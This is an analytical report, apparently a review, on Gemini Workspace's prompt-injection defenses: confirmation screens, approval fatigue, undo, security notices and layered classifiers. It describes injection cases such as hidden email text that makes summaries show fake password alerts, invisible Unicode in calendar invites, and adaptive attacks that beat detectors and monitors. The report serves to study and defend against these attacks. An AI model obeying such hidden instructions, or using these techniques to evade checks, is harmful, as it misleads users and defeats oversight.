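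A card with a button is hard to miss for someone looking at the screen. A question inside a longer chat reply is easier to overlook, and a user who types "yes" underneath may be answering something else. With Spark, the user may not be there to confirm, since it can run up to 15 tasks at once and start scheduled tasks while the user is offline. Google warns that the user may then be unable to stop an unintended action. If Gemini does ask and waits for an answer, the lease stays where it is until the user comes back.

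A confirmation request doesn't protect a user who notices it but misunderstands it. In research published in June 2026, SafeBreach found that Gemini could register a user's approval even when the user had not understood the question. Google had confirmed a fix in November 2025.

People can also misunderstand a request because it describes the action badly. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyzed 290 reports about AI agents that work with files and found that uninformative requests contributed to 31 of them. These requests showed a command but not what it would do to the user's files. Workspace has an advantage because most people know what it means to send an email or delete a meeting.

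In the lease example, the user has to see the address because it is the only thing wrong with the email. If Gemini writes the confirmation request in its own words, the injection can influence that text too, and the user may read "Send the lease to your landlord?" above an email addressed to someone else. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues, 2026) recommends displaying the tool, file and recipient recorded by a trusted monitor instead of the agent's paraphrase. Google's preview card lets the user edit the email, so it presumably includes the real recipient field, but a user who glances at it may not notice that the address is slightly wrong.

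Sometimes an action is wrong even though every detail on the confirmation card is correct. In an example from Hossain and colleagues, a user tells an agent to send an auditor only the totals from some invoices. An injection makes the agent copy the full invoices into a report, and the agent then asks to send the report to the auditor. The recipient is correct and the file name looks normal, so the user would have to know how the agent made the file to see the problem.

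To test how much information people need to judge an agent's requests, one study had 80 volunteers make 960 decisions. Half of the requests violated the user's original instructions. Each volunteer used one of four versions of the approval screen.

| What the screen displayed | Harmful requests approved | Legitimate requests approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
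| The exact details of the action | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| The details, the user's instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, with the consequence in one statement | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

*Results from Hossain and colleagues, with 20 people for each screen.*

Exact details helped, but people who had them still approved more than four in ten harmful requests. The best screen quoted the user's original restriction and stated the combined effect of the earlier steps and the new one. Its lead over the full log could be due to chance because each group was small (the 95 percent interval for the adjusted difference runs from 19.7 points better to 3.8 points worse). The evidence for the overall trend is stronger. The best screen also took twice as long as the short description, and people rejected somewhat more legitimate requests with it.

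Finally, each approval should cover only one action. If the address in the lease email changes after the user approves it, the system should ask again. Gemini Agent has a "Confirm all" button, which is convenient when a plan has many harmless steps but makes it easy to approve a harmful one without reading it. In Workspace Studio, Google plans to let users approve some steps permanently. If that approval covered every future recipient, a user who approved an email to their landlord would also have approved later emails to strangers.

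A refusal needs the same care. One software practitioner interviewed for the study *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) refused several permission requests, but the agent continued the task another way. They couldn't tell whether it was still keeping to the limit they had tried to set. In the lease example, a user who refuses the email doesn't want Gemini to share the file with the same stranger through Drive.

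### Approval fatigue

Even a well-designed request fails if people approve it without reading. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* uses the term "approval fatigue" for when people click "approve" so often that they stop paying close attention. Claude Code is a programming agent from Anthropic, the company behind the Claude models.

Users of Claude Code approve 97 percent of its permission requests, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). Most of those commands are probably safe, but an experiment with 1,053 paid testers found that people often approve dangerous ones too. Partway through each tester's session, the request on screen was replaced with one for a clearly dangerous command, and only 13.6 percent of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17 percent early in a session and about 5 percent after 50 or more requests.

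Anthropic published these figures to explain why it was replacing most confirmation requests with an automated check, which blocked 89 percent of the same commands. The testers also worked in a test environment, where they risked less than in their own projects, and a line of code is harder to judge than an email. The exact numbers probably don't apply to Workspace, but the decline over a long session is more likely to.

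Fatigue can't be the whole explanation, because the testers missed about five in six dangerous commands even early on. Yan found something similar with people who don't work in software. In one group, 34 people supervised a simulated day of email, calendar and travel tasks and had to approve or deny each of the agent's 18 actions. Seven of the actions went beyond what the user had asked for, and the group approved those seven 40.3 percent of the time.

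Some of those approvals were sensible. Thirty of the 34 people let the agent call the airport to confirm a flight, which many travelers would appreciate. Excluding that action, the rate falls to 32 percent. But about a third also let the agent read private messages or permanently delete an old timesheet, though the task required neither.

Another group of 44 people received only 10 requests, because a model handled the other actions automatically. They approved 46.1 percent of the same seven actions, so fewer requests didn't make them more careful. People in every group still reported feeling highly in control. The agent in this study overreached without any attacker involved, and nothing real was at stake, so the percentages are only a rough guide to how people would respond to an injection.

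Cutting the number of requests still seems worthwhile for people who use an assistant all day, but people also need to be able to judge each request. Claude Code users reject 39 percent of the plans it presents for approval, compared with 3 percent of individual permission requests. They may reject a plan because they want the work done differently, but they are evidently reading it. A draft email on a preview card is closer to a plan than to a line of code, which favors Google's design.

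Software can also decide the clear cases without human review. When Hossain and colleagues let their monitor block actions automatically, the number of malicious runs in which one agent did something unauthorized fell from 52 to 6 out of 120. They suggest asking people only when the monitor lacks the evidence to decide.

Companies should not assume that a long run of approvals shows growing trust. *Let the Agent Do It?* argues that it may instead reflect habit, fatigue or pressure to keep moving. In Workspace Studio, a user might choose permanent approval because the flow has proved reliable or because they are tired of the requests. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* found that automatic approval contributed to 80 of its 290 reports. Some users had switched off the requests entirely because they would otherwise have had to answer hundreds per session.

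### Countdown, report and undo

Nassi and colleagues propose three ways to involve the user without requiring a click for every action. The assistant could show a countdown with a cancel button, report each action after completing it, or let the user undo it.

A countdown interrupts people less than a confirmation request, but if the user ignores it, Gemini sends the lease instead of holding it. A countdown therefore doesn't protect someone who is driving, in a meeting or asleep while a scheduled task runs. Nassi and colleagues recommend it only as a last resort, and they leave it out of their estimate of the remaining risk because it makes the user responsible for stopping the attack.

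A report comes too late to prevent an action, but it tells the user that it happened. Someone who learns that Gemini has emailed their lease to a stranger can at least warn the landlord. Reports are most useful with an undo option. If Gemini opens a window in the user's home, for example, Nassi and colleagues would give the user a button to close it.

Google already lets users undo some of Gemini's actions. After the Gemini app changes a calendar, the user can select Undo in the notification. Google notes that Undo can't recall an email already sent to an event's guests, and that Gemini can't undo an event created while Gemini Live, its voice conversation mode, was running in the background. With Spark, the user follows a link to the Workspace app and reverses the change there by hand.

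Undo can restore a deleted appointment but can't reverse a leak, because a stranger who has read a file still knows its contents after its old sharing settings are restored. *Let the Agent Do It?* suggests that permission requests should tell users whether they can recover from an action, with stronger warnings or an extra confirmation when they can't. Google could go further and replace confirmation with undo for private changes that are easy to reverse. People would then see fewer requests, and those would be for actions like sending the lease.

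Undo only helps if the user notices the problem in time. Someone may not notice that an appointment is gone until its time has passed.

### Why confirmation can't stop a misleading answer

Asking for confirmation doesn't protect the user from a false sentence in a summary, because there is no action to approve. Nassi and colleagues recommend requiring confirmation for operations that involve outside data, but they don't list it as a remedy for spam, phishing and abusive text in Gemini's answers.

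Asking users to approve every summary wouldn't help either, because they would have to read all 20 emails to judge whether a summary of them is accurate.

A misleading answer can also make a later confirmation ineffective. Suppose Gemini's summary lists an attacker's address as the landlord's new email address. The user asks Gemini to send the lease there, and the preview card shows the same address. The user reads the card carefully, understands it and approves only that email, but the lease still goes to the attacker.

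## Warning notices and misleading answers

In the lease example, the user never learns that the summary was false. Google's fifth defense, the security notice, is meant to tell users about attacks, but Gemini shows one only when another defense has detected something.

### What the user sees

In Google's example of the notice, a user asks Gemini in Docs to summarize a file. Gemini detects suspicious content and gives no summary. The user sees a yellow banner, a statement that Gemini's response has been removed, and a "Learn more" link to a help page. If Gemini excludes only some of the material, the user gets a warning and a partial answer.

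On the help page, Google advises Workspace users to heed warnings in Gmail, avoid links from untrustworthy sources and be careful with files from people they don't know. Users can report an email as phishing, report a file as abusive, or send feedback on Gemini's answer. For the standalone Gemini app, Google also urges caution with other people's public Gemini chats and with web apps made in Gemini's Canvas feature.

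Google says it wants users to learn about the attacks it has stopped so they can watch for similar ones. That would work best if the notice identified the email or file responsible, but Google doesn't say whether it does. Someone who asks for a summary of 20 emails and learns that Gemini left one out needs to know which one, either to distrust the sender or to read a harmless email that Gemini excluded by mistake. Reporting a malicious email can also protect other people, since Gemini can't read messages that Google has already identified as spam.

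The notice doesn't stop anything itself. It may even give false reassurance, because people who are used to seeing a banner when something is wrong could assume an answer without one is safe. Google's advice doesn't correct this, since it is mostly about other people's emails, links and files. The only advice about Gemini's own answers is to send feedback on a bad one, which requires the user to notice that it's bad.

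### Tests in Gmail, Slides and Drive

Misleading answers were a known problem before Google described the notices. *New Gemini for Workspace Vulnerability Enabling Phishing & Content Manipulation* (Martin and Yeung, September 2024) reported HiddenLayer's tests in three Workspace apps.

In Gmail, researchers sent themselves an email containing hidden instructions and asked Gemini about it. Gemini greeted them by a silly name and wrote a poem. In a more serious test, a second email caused Gemini to answer a question about a holiday itinerary by saying that the user's password wasn't safe and telling them to change it at a web address that resembled Google's.

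In Slides, they put the instructions in a presentation's speaker notes, and Gemini's summary became a poem built around the words of a 1980s pop song. Gemini generated the summary automatically, so the user didn't have to request it.

The Drive test is the most worrying because the injection was in a different file from the one the user asked about, so being careful about which files to summarize wouldn't have protected the user. Martin and Yeung asked for a summary of a rant about bananas and got the output specified in the other file. They also got an injection to work from a file shared by another account, after giving the file a name that matched the request.

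Google marked the Gmail report "Won't Fix (Intended Behavior)". It gave much the same answer about Slides and said it already knew about the issue. The label probably meant that Gemini was designed to read the content and let it influence the answer, not that Google intended Gemini to send people to fake password pages. If so, there was no separate bug to fix.

Google had used a different label a few months earlier. According to WithSecure's *When your AI Assistant has an evil twin*, WithSecure told Google in May 2024 about a social engineering attack through Gemini, meaning one that tricks a person rather than breaking into a system. Google called it an "Abuse Risk" and said it wouldn't fix it for the time being. WithSecure acknowledged that such attacks are hard to stop and noted that Google's protections had blocked its attempts to leak data through links.

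Martin and Yeung published individual demonstrations without success rates, and Google has replaced the underlying models several times since, so their tests provide little evidence about Gemini today. But the Gmail attack reappeared in a very similar form less than ten months later.

### A false security alert

*Phishing For Gemini* (Figueroa, 10 July 2025) describes an attack that a researcher submitted to 0DIN, Mozilla's program for reporting flaws in generative AI. The attacker sends an email containing hidden text. When the recipient selects "Summarize this email", Gemini's summary includes a warning that their Gmail password is no longer secure and a phone number to call. If the recipient calls, the attacker can ask for the password.

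Figueroa says this worked mainly because Gemini received the email's underlying code, including text the user couldn't see, and because that text was presented as coming from an administrator. The second reason fits Ye and colleagues' finding that models infer who is speaking partly from how the text sounds.

The false alert also resembled the real security warnings that Google shows in Gemini. A real warning is a separate banner with a link to a help page, while the false alert was part of the summary. A user who knew this might spot the fake, but Google doesn't explain the difference in its help pages.

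Google didn't call this intended behavior. TechBriefly's *How hackers can weaponize Gemini's summary feature* (2025) reports that Google was strengthening its defenses and had seen no evidence of the attack in real use. In IT Brew's *In summary* (2025), Workspace spokesperson Ross Richendrfer called defending against prompt injection a "continued priority".

The attack still worked five days after the disclosure, as shown in screenshots from 15 July that Kev Breen of the security company Immersive shared with IT Brew. Gemini's answer now began with a note that the email's signature included a hidden warning. This was a partial improvement, because users could see that the warning came from the email, but an anxious reader might still take a "hidden warning" more seriously than an ordinary one.

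A journalist also reproduced the attack for Startup Daily's *Scammers can now use Google Gemini for phishing as pretend AI* and found that the false alert could include links to active phishing sites. URL redaction should have removed those links if it was running and Safe Browsing had listed the sites.

Breen's appears to be the latest public test of this attack on Gmail. Google has updated its classifiers and models since then, so the original email probably no longer works, but a reworded version might. Microsoft has had the same problem. Underhill (2026), in *AI Email Summaries Create a New Phishing Attack Surface*, reports that researchers at the security company Permiso could insert phishing alerts into Copilot's email summaries.

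Criminals have since begun to try this. *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026) describes a phishing campaign that the security company Barracuda analyzed in October 2026. The email contained hidden instructions for the recipient's AI assistant and a password-protected attachment for the recipient to open. If the recipient overlooked the email, the assistant's summary could present it as legitimate or urgent. In another real-world example from Barracuda, an invoice email contained instructions for the assistant to add a false priority action that changed a supplier's payment details.

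Barracuda didn't say how widespread the campaign was, and Mascellino doesn't report which assistants, if any, followed the instructions. The campaign is therefore evidence that attackers are trying to manipulate summaries, not that they have succeeded with Gemini. But Google's July 2025 reassurance is out of date for email in general.

### Characters that people can't see

The email that made Gemini recommend a fake phone shop came from research by Viktor Markopoulos of the security company FireTail. He used a technique called ASCII smuggling, which hides text in characters that computers can process but people can't see. The characters belong to Unicode, the standard that gives each character a number. According to ITPro's *Cyber criminals are adapting ASCII smuggling for mass phishing campaigns*, these invisible characters were originally meant to label languages and are now largely obsolete.

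The researcher's own account, *ASCII Smuggling in Google Gemini* by vict0ni, includes tests with calendar invitations. In one, Google Calendar displayed the title "Meeting", but Gemini told the user that the meeting was optional. In others, hidden text changed the description, the meeting link and the organizer's identity in Gemini's answer. The user didn't have to accept the invitation first.

A misleading answer doesn't need an urgent warning, phone number or link. For example, if Gemini wrongly says that a meeting is optional, a user who believes it misses the meeting.

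FireTail reported the problem on 18 September 2025 and received a "no action" response, according to Cybersecurity News' *ASCII Smuggling Attack Gemini*. BGR's *Google Has No Plans To Fix This Terrifying Gemini Security Vulnerability* quotes Google saying the attack "can only result in social engineering". In FireTail's tests, Grok and DeepSeek were also vulnerable, but ChatGPT, Copilot and Claude resisted the attack.

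FireTail tested Gemini again with a related technique that hides text inside an emoji (*Peek-A-Boo! 🫣 Emoji Smuggling and Modern LLMs*, 2026). Gemini detected the unusual characters but couldn't decode them until the visible part of the prompt explained how. It then followed the hidden instructions. The testers gave Gemini the prompt directly, so the result doesn't show whether the calendar attack still works. It may well, since there is no public sign that Google has reversed its decision on that attack, but the evidence is from 2025.

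Removing these characters would also help spam filters. ITPro reports that Microsoft saw a sharp rise in emails containing them in February 2026, which lasted about three months. In the emails that Microsoft sampled, the senders had used the characters to split up common financial words so that spam filters wouldn't recognize them. None of those emails contained instructions for AI assistants. A filter that removed the characters would restore the words, whether or not an assistant ever read the email.

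### Why a false answer is hard to spot

Neither a filter nor a person can reliably recognize a false answer from its wording, because the same words could be true of a different email.

Ben Gibney, a researcher at the security company Forcepoint, demonstrated this with a summarizer built on Claude Haiku 4.5. In *An Invisible HTML Payload Silently Hijacked Every Email Summarizer Run*, he compared two invoice emails that looked almost identical to the recipient. One contained 472 hidden characters, nearly half of the text the model received. He decided in advance what would count as success and ran each email through the summarizer ten times.

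All ten summaries of the altered email gave the attacker's amount, 46,200 euros, more than five times the real one. They also gave a false date and left out the real deadline. None mentioned the hidden text or any conflict between the two versions. Each looked like a normal invoice summary.

Gibney set the model to give nearly the same output each time, so a perfect score over ten runs is little more evidence than a single success. The summarizer also had no protections, unlike Gemini. The experiment is therefore more useful as an example of a successful attack than as an estimate of how often one would succeed.

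Figueroa suggests scanning Gemini's answers for phone numbers, web addresses and urgent security language. This would catch the false password alert, but it would also flag a summary of a dentist's email that includes the office number. It would miss the wrong invoice amount and the optional meeting, since a summary of an honest email could contain either.

People have fewer clues that something is wrong when they read a summary than when they read the email itself. They might notice a strange sender address or clumsy writing in an ordinary phishing email, but Gemini can turn the same claim into a clear sentence in Google's own interface. Android Central's *Turns out Gmail's AI email summaries aren't as secure as we thought* says most people won't think to question a summary from Google's AI. That is plausible, but none of these tests measured how much more readily people believe a false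 claim from Gemini than from a stranger.

Users can catch many false answers by opening the original email, where they would see the real invoice amount or find no visible password alert. But people ask for summaries to avoid reading every email, so they are unlikely to check unless something seems wrong.

A better solution is to give the model only the text that the user can see, as Gibney recommends. Figueroa also recommends removing invisible text before it reaches the model. This would have stopped the false password alert and the invisible characters in calendar invitations, however the attacker worded the hidden instructions. It wouldn't necessarily have stopped the Slides attack, because people can read speaker notes if they open them.

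Software would still have to determine what counts as visible. Dennis Xu, an analyst at the research company Gartner, asked IT Brew what would happen if an attacker used gray text instead of white, or put a visible command in a 20-page email. Few people would notice either. But the attacker would have to leave the command where the recipient could see it, which makes the attack riskier to attempt and easier to report.

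Figueroa also recommends that assistants visually separate their own words from material they quote. This would help even when the false claim is visible to the user. "Your password is unsafe" sounds like a warning from Google, but adding "The sender says" prompts the user to consider who the sender is.

### Security flaw or social engineering?

Google and the researchers disagree about whether a misleading answer is a security flaw. The rules of Google's reward programs help explain its position, though they have changed since the first reports.

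Before October 2025, Google's *Abuse Vulnerability Reward Program Rules* covered AI reports. Google distinguished security vulnerabilities, which need a fix, from abuse risks, which are often inherent in a useful feature. An injection qualified if the victim couldn't see it and it changed their account or something they owned. It also qualified if it influenced a tool whose response was used to make decisions that directly affected victims. Misleading or incorrect content "in your own session" didn't qualify.

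The false password alert doesn't fit these rules neatly. It changes nothing in the victim's account, but a stranger caused it to appear in the victim's session, so it isn't content that someone produced in their own. The exclusion seems to have been written for a different case, in which a person gets a chatbot to say something absurd and reports it. According to TechRadar's *Google launches AI bug bounties*, two Google managers later admitted that the scope "wasn't always clear".

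Google announced a separate AI Vulnerability Reward Program on 6 October 2025, in Kotsovinos and Flynn (2025), *How we’re securing the AI frontier*. SecurityWeek's *Google Offers Up to $20,000 in New AI Bug Bounty Program* reports that the program excludes prompt injections, but heise online's *Google* lists invisible injections that change a victim's account among the qualifying bugs. Both can be correct if Google pays for an injection's effects rather than the injection itself.

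For Google's main products, including Gmail and the Gemini app, the company's AI Vulnerability Reward Program offers a top base reward of $20,000 for reporting attacks that change a victim's account or data and $15,000 for those that leak sensitive data. Attacks that enable phishing earn at most $5,000, according to McDade (2025), in *Google Launches AI Vulnerability Reward Program With Payouts Up To $30,000*.

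Even the phishing category is narrow. According to SecurityWeek, the attack must be convincing, and the attacker must be able to inject HTML that persists on a Google-branded site, affects other users and appears without a warning that it is user-generated. A false alert in a Gmail summary is convincing, appears in a Google product and affects another user, but it probably doesn't qualify because it is ordinary text, not HTML.

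Google argues that people should report problems with content through the product rather than through a reward program. This makes sense for ordinary mistakes, because language models make too many for engineers to fix each one separately. An attacker can also send a false password alert without Gemini's help, and the earlier rules excluded harm that was already possible with other tools. With or without Gemini, the victim still has to believe the alert and call the number.

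The researchers focus more on what happens before the victim makes that choice. Martin and Yeung stress that an outsider can take control of Gemini and make it display any message. In the FireTail tests, vict0ni objects that Gemini reads an invitation before the user decides whether to accept it, so rejecting a stranger's invitation comes too late.

The researchers have the better argument when the text is hidden. Persuading someone to call a phone number is social engineering, but Gemini reading text that its user can't see is a technical fault. Three competing assistants resisted FireTail's invisible characters, so a defense is evidently practical. Hidden text also gives the attacker an advantage over an ordinary phishing email, because the false statement appears to come from Google. Google's argument is stronger when Gemini accurately summarizes a visible lie, since the user could have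 been fooled by reading the email.

Google can refuse to pay for a report and still work on the problem, as its response to the 0DIN disclosure suggests. But the reward rules probably influence the defenses, because Google's content classifiers learn from attacks that researchers report through the program. Rewards motivate these researchers. At an invitation-only event in Tokyo in April 2025, they filed more than 70 reports on AI products and earned over $400,000, according to Google's *VRP 2025 Year in Review*. If misleading answers earn little or nothing, researchers will probably report fewer of them, leaving the classifiers with fewer examples. User feedback could supply some of the missing examples, but only from people who realized that Gemini had misled them.

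## Updating, testing and combining the layers

Researchers' reports to the reward program also go into a catalog of attacks, which Google uses to update every layer. Gavish described the cycle in April 2026, from discovering an attack to testing a new defense.

### From a reported attack to a new defense

Researchers' reports are one of four sources for the catalog. Google also has specialists who attack its products while acting as realistic users, and it runs programs that generate injections automatically. Finally, it looks for publicly known attacks in blogs, press releases and social media, then tries them on its own products.

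The automated programs refine an injection by trial and error, like the attacks in DeepMind's experiments. According to Google's *How we estimate the risk from prompt injection attacks on AI systems*, they then test the finished injection on many conversations, because a real attacker wouldn't know what the user and the assistant had been discussing. Google wants these attacks to be as strong as possible, since a system that withstands a weak attack may still be easy to break.

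When a new attack arrives, Google's staff reproduce it, check whether the catalog already contains it, label its technique and the harm it causes, and assign it to a team. A tool called Simula then generates variants of the attack. For example, if an invitation made Gemini copy private meetings into a new event, a variant might use different wording, hide the instruction in a shared document, or ask for emails instead of meetings.

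Google uses the variants to update several defenses. Engineers retrain the classifiers on one part of the data and check them on the rest. For defenses that are language models following written instructions, they revise the instructions and keep the versions that score better. They also train Gemini on the new attacks. They can update the fixed rules in the Policy Engine just by changing its settings.

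Gavish says that this workflow has "boosted synthetic data generation by 75%". The figure measures how much artificial training and test data Google produces, or perhaps how fast it produces it, not how many attacks it stops. The extra data could help much more if it contains new kinds of attack than if it only rewords existing ones. Gavish gives no attack success rate or false positive rate.

Testing a classifier on data it wasn't trained on is standard practice, and it prevents the classifier from scoring well through memorization alone. How much the test shows about new attacks depends on how Google divides the data. If Simula writes 1,000 variants of the invitation and 800 go into training, the other 200 will closely resemble the training examples. A good score on those 200 would be little evidence that the classifier can detect an attack based on a new idea. A harder test would keep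 every variant of certain attacks out of the training data. Gavish doesn't say which method Google uses.

### Testing with and without each defense

Google tests a new defense by simulating attacks on many Workspace features, in Gmail, Docs and other apps, using a standard set of test material. It runs the whole test once with the defense and once without it, then measures the defense's effect as the difference between the two attack success rates.

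This has one advantage over almost any test that outsiders can run, because Google can test the product people use, with every layer in place. Most published results are for a model alone or with one added defense.

Removing one layer at a time can still be misleading. Suppose that a classifier and a reminder each stop the same 300 of 1,000 simulated attacks. Each looks useless when switched off alone, because the other still stops all 300, but switching off both lets all 300 through. Google would have to test combinations of layers to detect this overlap. Four of the five defenses can stop an attack (the security notice only reports one), so there are 16 combinations, few enough to test automatically.

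A more serious limitation is that the simulated attacks mostly predate the defense under test, because they come from the catalog. Google DeepMind warned in 2025 that relying on defenses tested only against static attacks gives "a false sense of security". Google's automated programs can attack the updated product and add whatever they find to the catalog, so the cycle should adapt over time. It is unclear whether they do this before a new defense reaches users or only afterward.

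Gavish also doesn't describe a matching test on harmless emails and files. Google presumably runs one, because the easiest way to improve a classifier's score against attacks is to have it flag more of everything.

### How long fixes have taken

Few of the attacks on Gemini have a public date for both the report and the fix. Three that do are in the table.

| Attack | Reported to Google | Google's confirmation | Time between |
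|---|---|---|---|
| Image leak in Bard | 19 September 2023 | 19 October 2023 | 30 days |
| Calendar attacks by Nassi and colleagues | 22 February 2025 | June 2025 | About 4 months |
| Notification attacks by SafeBreach | 17 August 2025 | 14 November 2025 | 89 days |

*Dates on which Google confirmed its fixes or described them to the researchers.*

These are upper limits, because Google may have had a fix in place for weeks before it told the researchers. The fastest known response was in AI Studio, where Google stopped an image leak within 24 hours of a public complaint by changing how the site displayed image code. That fits Gavish's claim that fixed rules are quicker to change than models, though a handful of cases can't establish it. Google also invites researchers to attack some features before release, which can keep the flaws they find from reaching users.

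SafeBreach reports that Google fixed the notification attacks by improving its content classifier. The confirmation that this fix covers the injections and delayed actions in the report is good evidence that those attacks no longer work, and probably that close variants don't either. It doesn't establish whether Google also repaired the check that wrongly treated a user's "yes" as permission to open a window. If a new injection gets past the classifier, that check might be as easy to bypass as it was in August 2025.

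Google's fix for the earlier calendar attacks shows the limits of such repairs. Google had tested the fix on many variations of the attacks, and it blocked the old technique, but Yair soon got around it with a new one. Simula can generate far more variations, but Yair found the bypass by working out what the new check examined.

Yair concludes that the architecture is at fault. He argues that as long as one model works as a "magic box" that takes instructions from both the system and the user, an attacker only has to look legitimate enough. Google answers that the attacker has to get past several defenses.

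### The argument for layers

According to Google's June 2025 post on the five defenses, *Mitigating prompt injection attacks*, layering forces attackers to use methods that are easier to identify or need more resources. DeepMind similarly describes the goal as making attacks "much harder, costlier, and more complex".

The usual argument for this has three premises. Each layer stops some attacks, the layers don't tend to fail on the same attacks, and an attacker has to pass all of them. If so, the failure rates multiply. Three layers that each miss 20 percent of attacks would together miss only

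0.2 × 0.2 × 0.2 = 0.008,

or 0.8 percent. No single layer has to be very good, which is what makes the argument attractive.

Plenty of evidence shows that each layer stops some attacks, but no layer stops every kind. Any calculation of the protection against a false sentence in a summary can include only the classifier, the reminder and the hardened model.

The weakest premise is that the layers fail on different attacks. An injection that reads like an ordinary request from the user is hard for the classifier to flag, and it is hard for Gemini to ignore for the same reason. Suppose that 90 percent of attacks are crude and 10 percent are subtle, and that each of three layers misses 5 percent of the crude ones and 70 percent of the subtle ones. Tested separately, each layer misses 11.5 percent of all attacks:

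0.9 × 0.05 + 0.1 × 0.7 = 0.115.

Multiplying the three rates gives 0.115³, or about 0.15 percent. But the share that actually gets past all three is

0.9 × 0.05³ + 0.1 × 0.7³ ≈ 0.034,

or 3.4 percent, which is more than 20 times as high. Nearly all the successful attacks are subtle ones. An attacker who knows this will send nothing else, and about 34 percent of those get through.

The numbers are invented, but Google's update cycle gives a reason to expect something like this. Google uses the same catalog and synthetic data to improve the classifiers, the written instructions and the hardened model. This is efficient, since a reported attack leads to updates in all three, but none of them will have been updated for an attack that nobody has reported.

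Fixed rules fail for different reasons than classifiers do. A block on external images, for example, fails if the sanitizer misreads an unusual format, regardless of how persuasive the injection is. Adding such a rule to a classifier therefore probably helps more than adding a second classifier, provided the rule covers what the attacker wants to do.

That proviso matters because an attacker doesn't have to pass every layer. The classifier, the reminder and the hardened model stand in a line, and an injection must get through all of them. After that, private data can leave in an image, a link, an email, a calendar event or a request from the browsing tool, and the attacker needs only one of these. If three routes were each blocked with a probability of 90 percent, independently of one another, the chance that at least one was open would be

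1 − 0.9³ = 0.271,

or 27 percent. Miggo's calendar event and Tenable's browsing-tool leak both went around the restrictions on links and images. Extra layers at the entrance make every attack harder, but a strong defense on one exit may only send attackers to another.

### The one combination with published results

In *Lessons from Defending Gemini Against Indirect Prompt Injections*, DeepMind tested two defenses together on the calendar task from the earlier experiments, in which the attacker wants the user's passport number.

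| System | Attack success rate |
|---|---|
| Gemini 2.0, no defense | 100% |
| Gemini 2.5, hardened | 94.6% |
| Gemini 2.0 with a warning after the retrieved content | 10.8% |
| Gemini 2.5, hardened, with the warning | 6.2% |

*Results on the calendar task.*

Hardening alone hardly slowed this attack, while the warning alone stopped almost nine in ten attempts. If the two had independent effects, the combination would allow

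0.946 × 0.108 ≈ 0.102,

or 10.2 percent. The measured rate is about two fifths lower than that.

It is also close to the best result that two separate filters could produce. Hardening stopped only 5.4 percent of attempts, so even if the warning had missed every one of those, the rate would have fallen only from 10.8 to 5.4 percent. Two filters made in the same laboratory would be very unlikely to overlap so little.

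A better explanation is that the warning's effect depends on the model, because Gemini has to read the warning and act on it. DeepMind had trained Gemini 2.5 on responses that an earlier model gave when its prompt contained a warning. This hardening may have made the model much better at following warnings, even though it did little without one. Or Gemini 2.5 may follow instructions better than Gemini 2.0, with or without hardening. Testing the warning on an unhardened Gemini 2.5 would help to separate these explanations, but the comparison doesn't include that test.

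Chance probably doesn't account for the gap. DeepMind's rates for this task are all multiples of 0.2 percent, which suggests 500 test conversations. With 500, the margin of error on 6.2 percent is about two percentage points either way. But that margin only reflects which conversations happened to be in the test. The attack program also searches partly at random, so another run might have found a better injection.

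When the researchers report the 6.2 percent, they don't say whether the program searched for new injections with both defenses in place. This could matter a good deal, because against the warning alone, the same type of attack succeeded 1.2 percent of the time with injections prepared in advance and 10.8 percent once it could adapt. If DeepMind reused injections from another run, 6.2 percent is probably too low.

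Even taken at face value, 6.2 percent is one conversation in 16. Workspace's other layers, such as the classifiers and the approval step before an email goes out, should reduce that rate further. But the warning had an advantage because it forbade exactly what the attacker wanted. The result supports combining a trained model with a reminder, but it can't be used to estimate how well all of Google's layers work together.

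### Attacks built to beat the defense

*The Attacker Moves Second*, an October 2025 paper by Nasr and colleagues, is the strongest evidence against multiplying the layers' failure rates to estimate their combined protection. The researchers, including some from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, attacked 12 published defenses with methods adapted to each. Most of the defenses had attack success rates near zero in their original evaluations, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90 percent of the time against most of the 12.

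Besides the prompt-based defenses covered earlier, they tested detectors, models trained to resist injection, and defenses that depend on a secret.

| Defense | How it works | Adaptive attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Protect AI, PromptGuard and Model Armor | A separate detector screens the text | Over 90% for each |
| PIGuard | A separate detector screens the text | 71% |
| MetaSecAlign | Training teaches the model to ignore injections | 96% |
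| MELON | A second run with a different request reveals suspicious tool calls | 76%, or 95% if the attacker knows the design |

*Results from Nasr and colleagues for six of the 12 defenses.*

The researchers tested Model Armor, a Google product sold through Google Cloud, with Gemini 2.5 Pro behind it. The result can't be assumed to apply to the classifiers in Workspace. MetaSecAlign had reported that only 2 percent of ready-made attacks succeeded. MELON resembles the proposal by Nassi and colleagues to run a request twice and compare the outcomes. The attack program beat it by finding injections that took effect in the real run but not in the other.

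The conditions favored the attackers, who had unlimited computing power and saw each detector's confidence score after every attempt. Someone preparing an email for a Gmail user wouldn't see that score, but they could get a rougher signal by testing the injection on their own account, where Gemini shows a security notice when it detects one.

On a selected set of cases, the search program succeeded in 69 percent, while the human participants together succeeded in all of them. People also produced 123 successful injections against the detectors under the strictest setting.

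Nasr and colleagues conclude that stacking more detectors doesn't solve the problem, because their attacks got past the model and every detector, even in combination. This would be expected if the layers share blind spots. The conclusion applies to layers that judge text, but not to a rule against ever loading external images. The researchers still think detectors are worth keeping because they help against unsophisticated attacks.

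In image recognition, training a model on a fixed set of attacks gave little protection against new ones. Generating fresh attacks against the model during training worked better. Google's update cycle is somewhere between the two. Simula's variants start from known attacks, but the automated programs can search for new ones each time Google changes a defense. Shortening the cycle brings it closer to generating attacks during training.

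Google's before-and-after tests help choose between two versions of a defense, but a good score can't prove that the better one is secure. As Nasr and colleagues put it, an evaluation can only "*fail to prove that the defense is broken*", so its value depends on how hard the testers tried to break it.

### Success rates for recent models

A large public contest produced a much lower figure for Gemini than DeepMind's own test did. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports that 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. An attack counted only if it made the agent do something harmful, and usually the agent's reply also had to show no sign of it. In one scenario, the user asked about urgent emails, and the injection was meant to make the agent mark a message about an important deadline as read and leave it out of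 the summary.

All 13 models failed at least some of the time. Claude Opus 4.5 had the lowest attack success rate, at 0.5 percent, and Gemini 2.5 Pro had the highest, at 8.5 percent.

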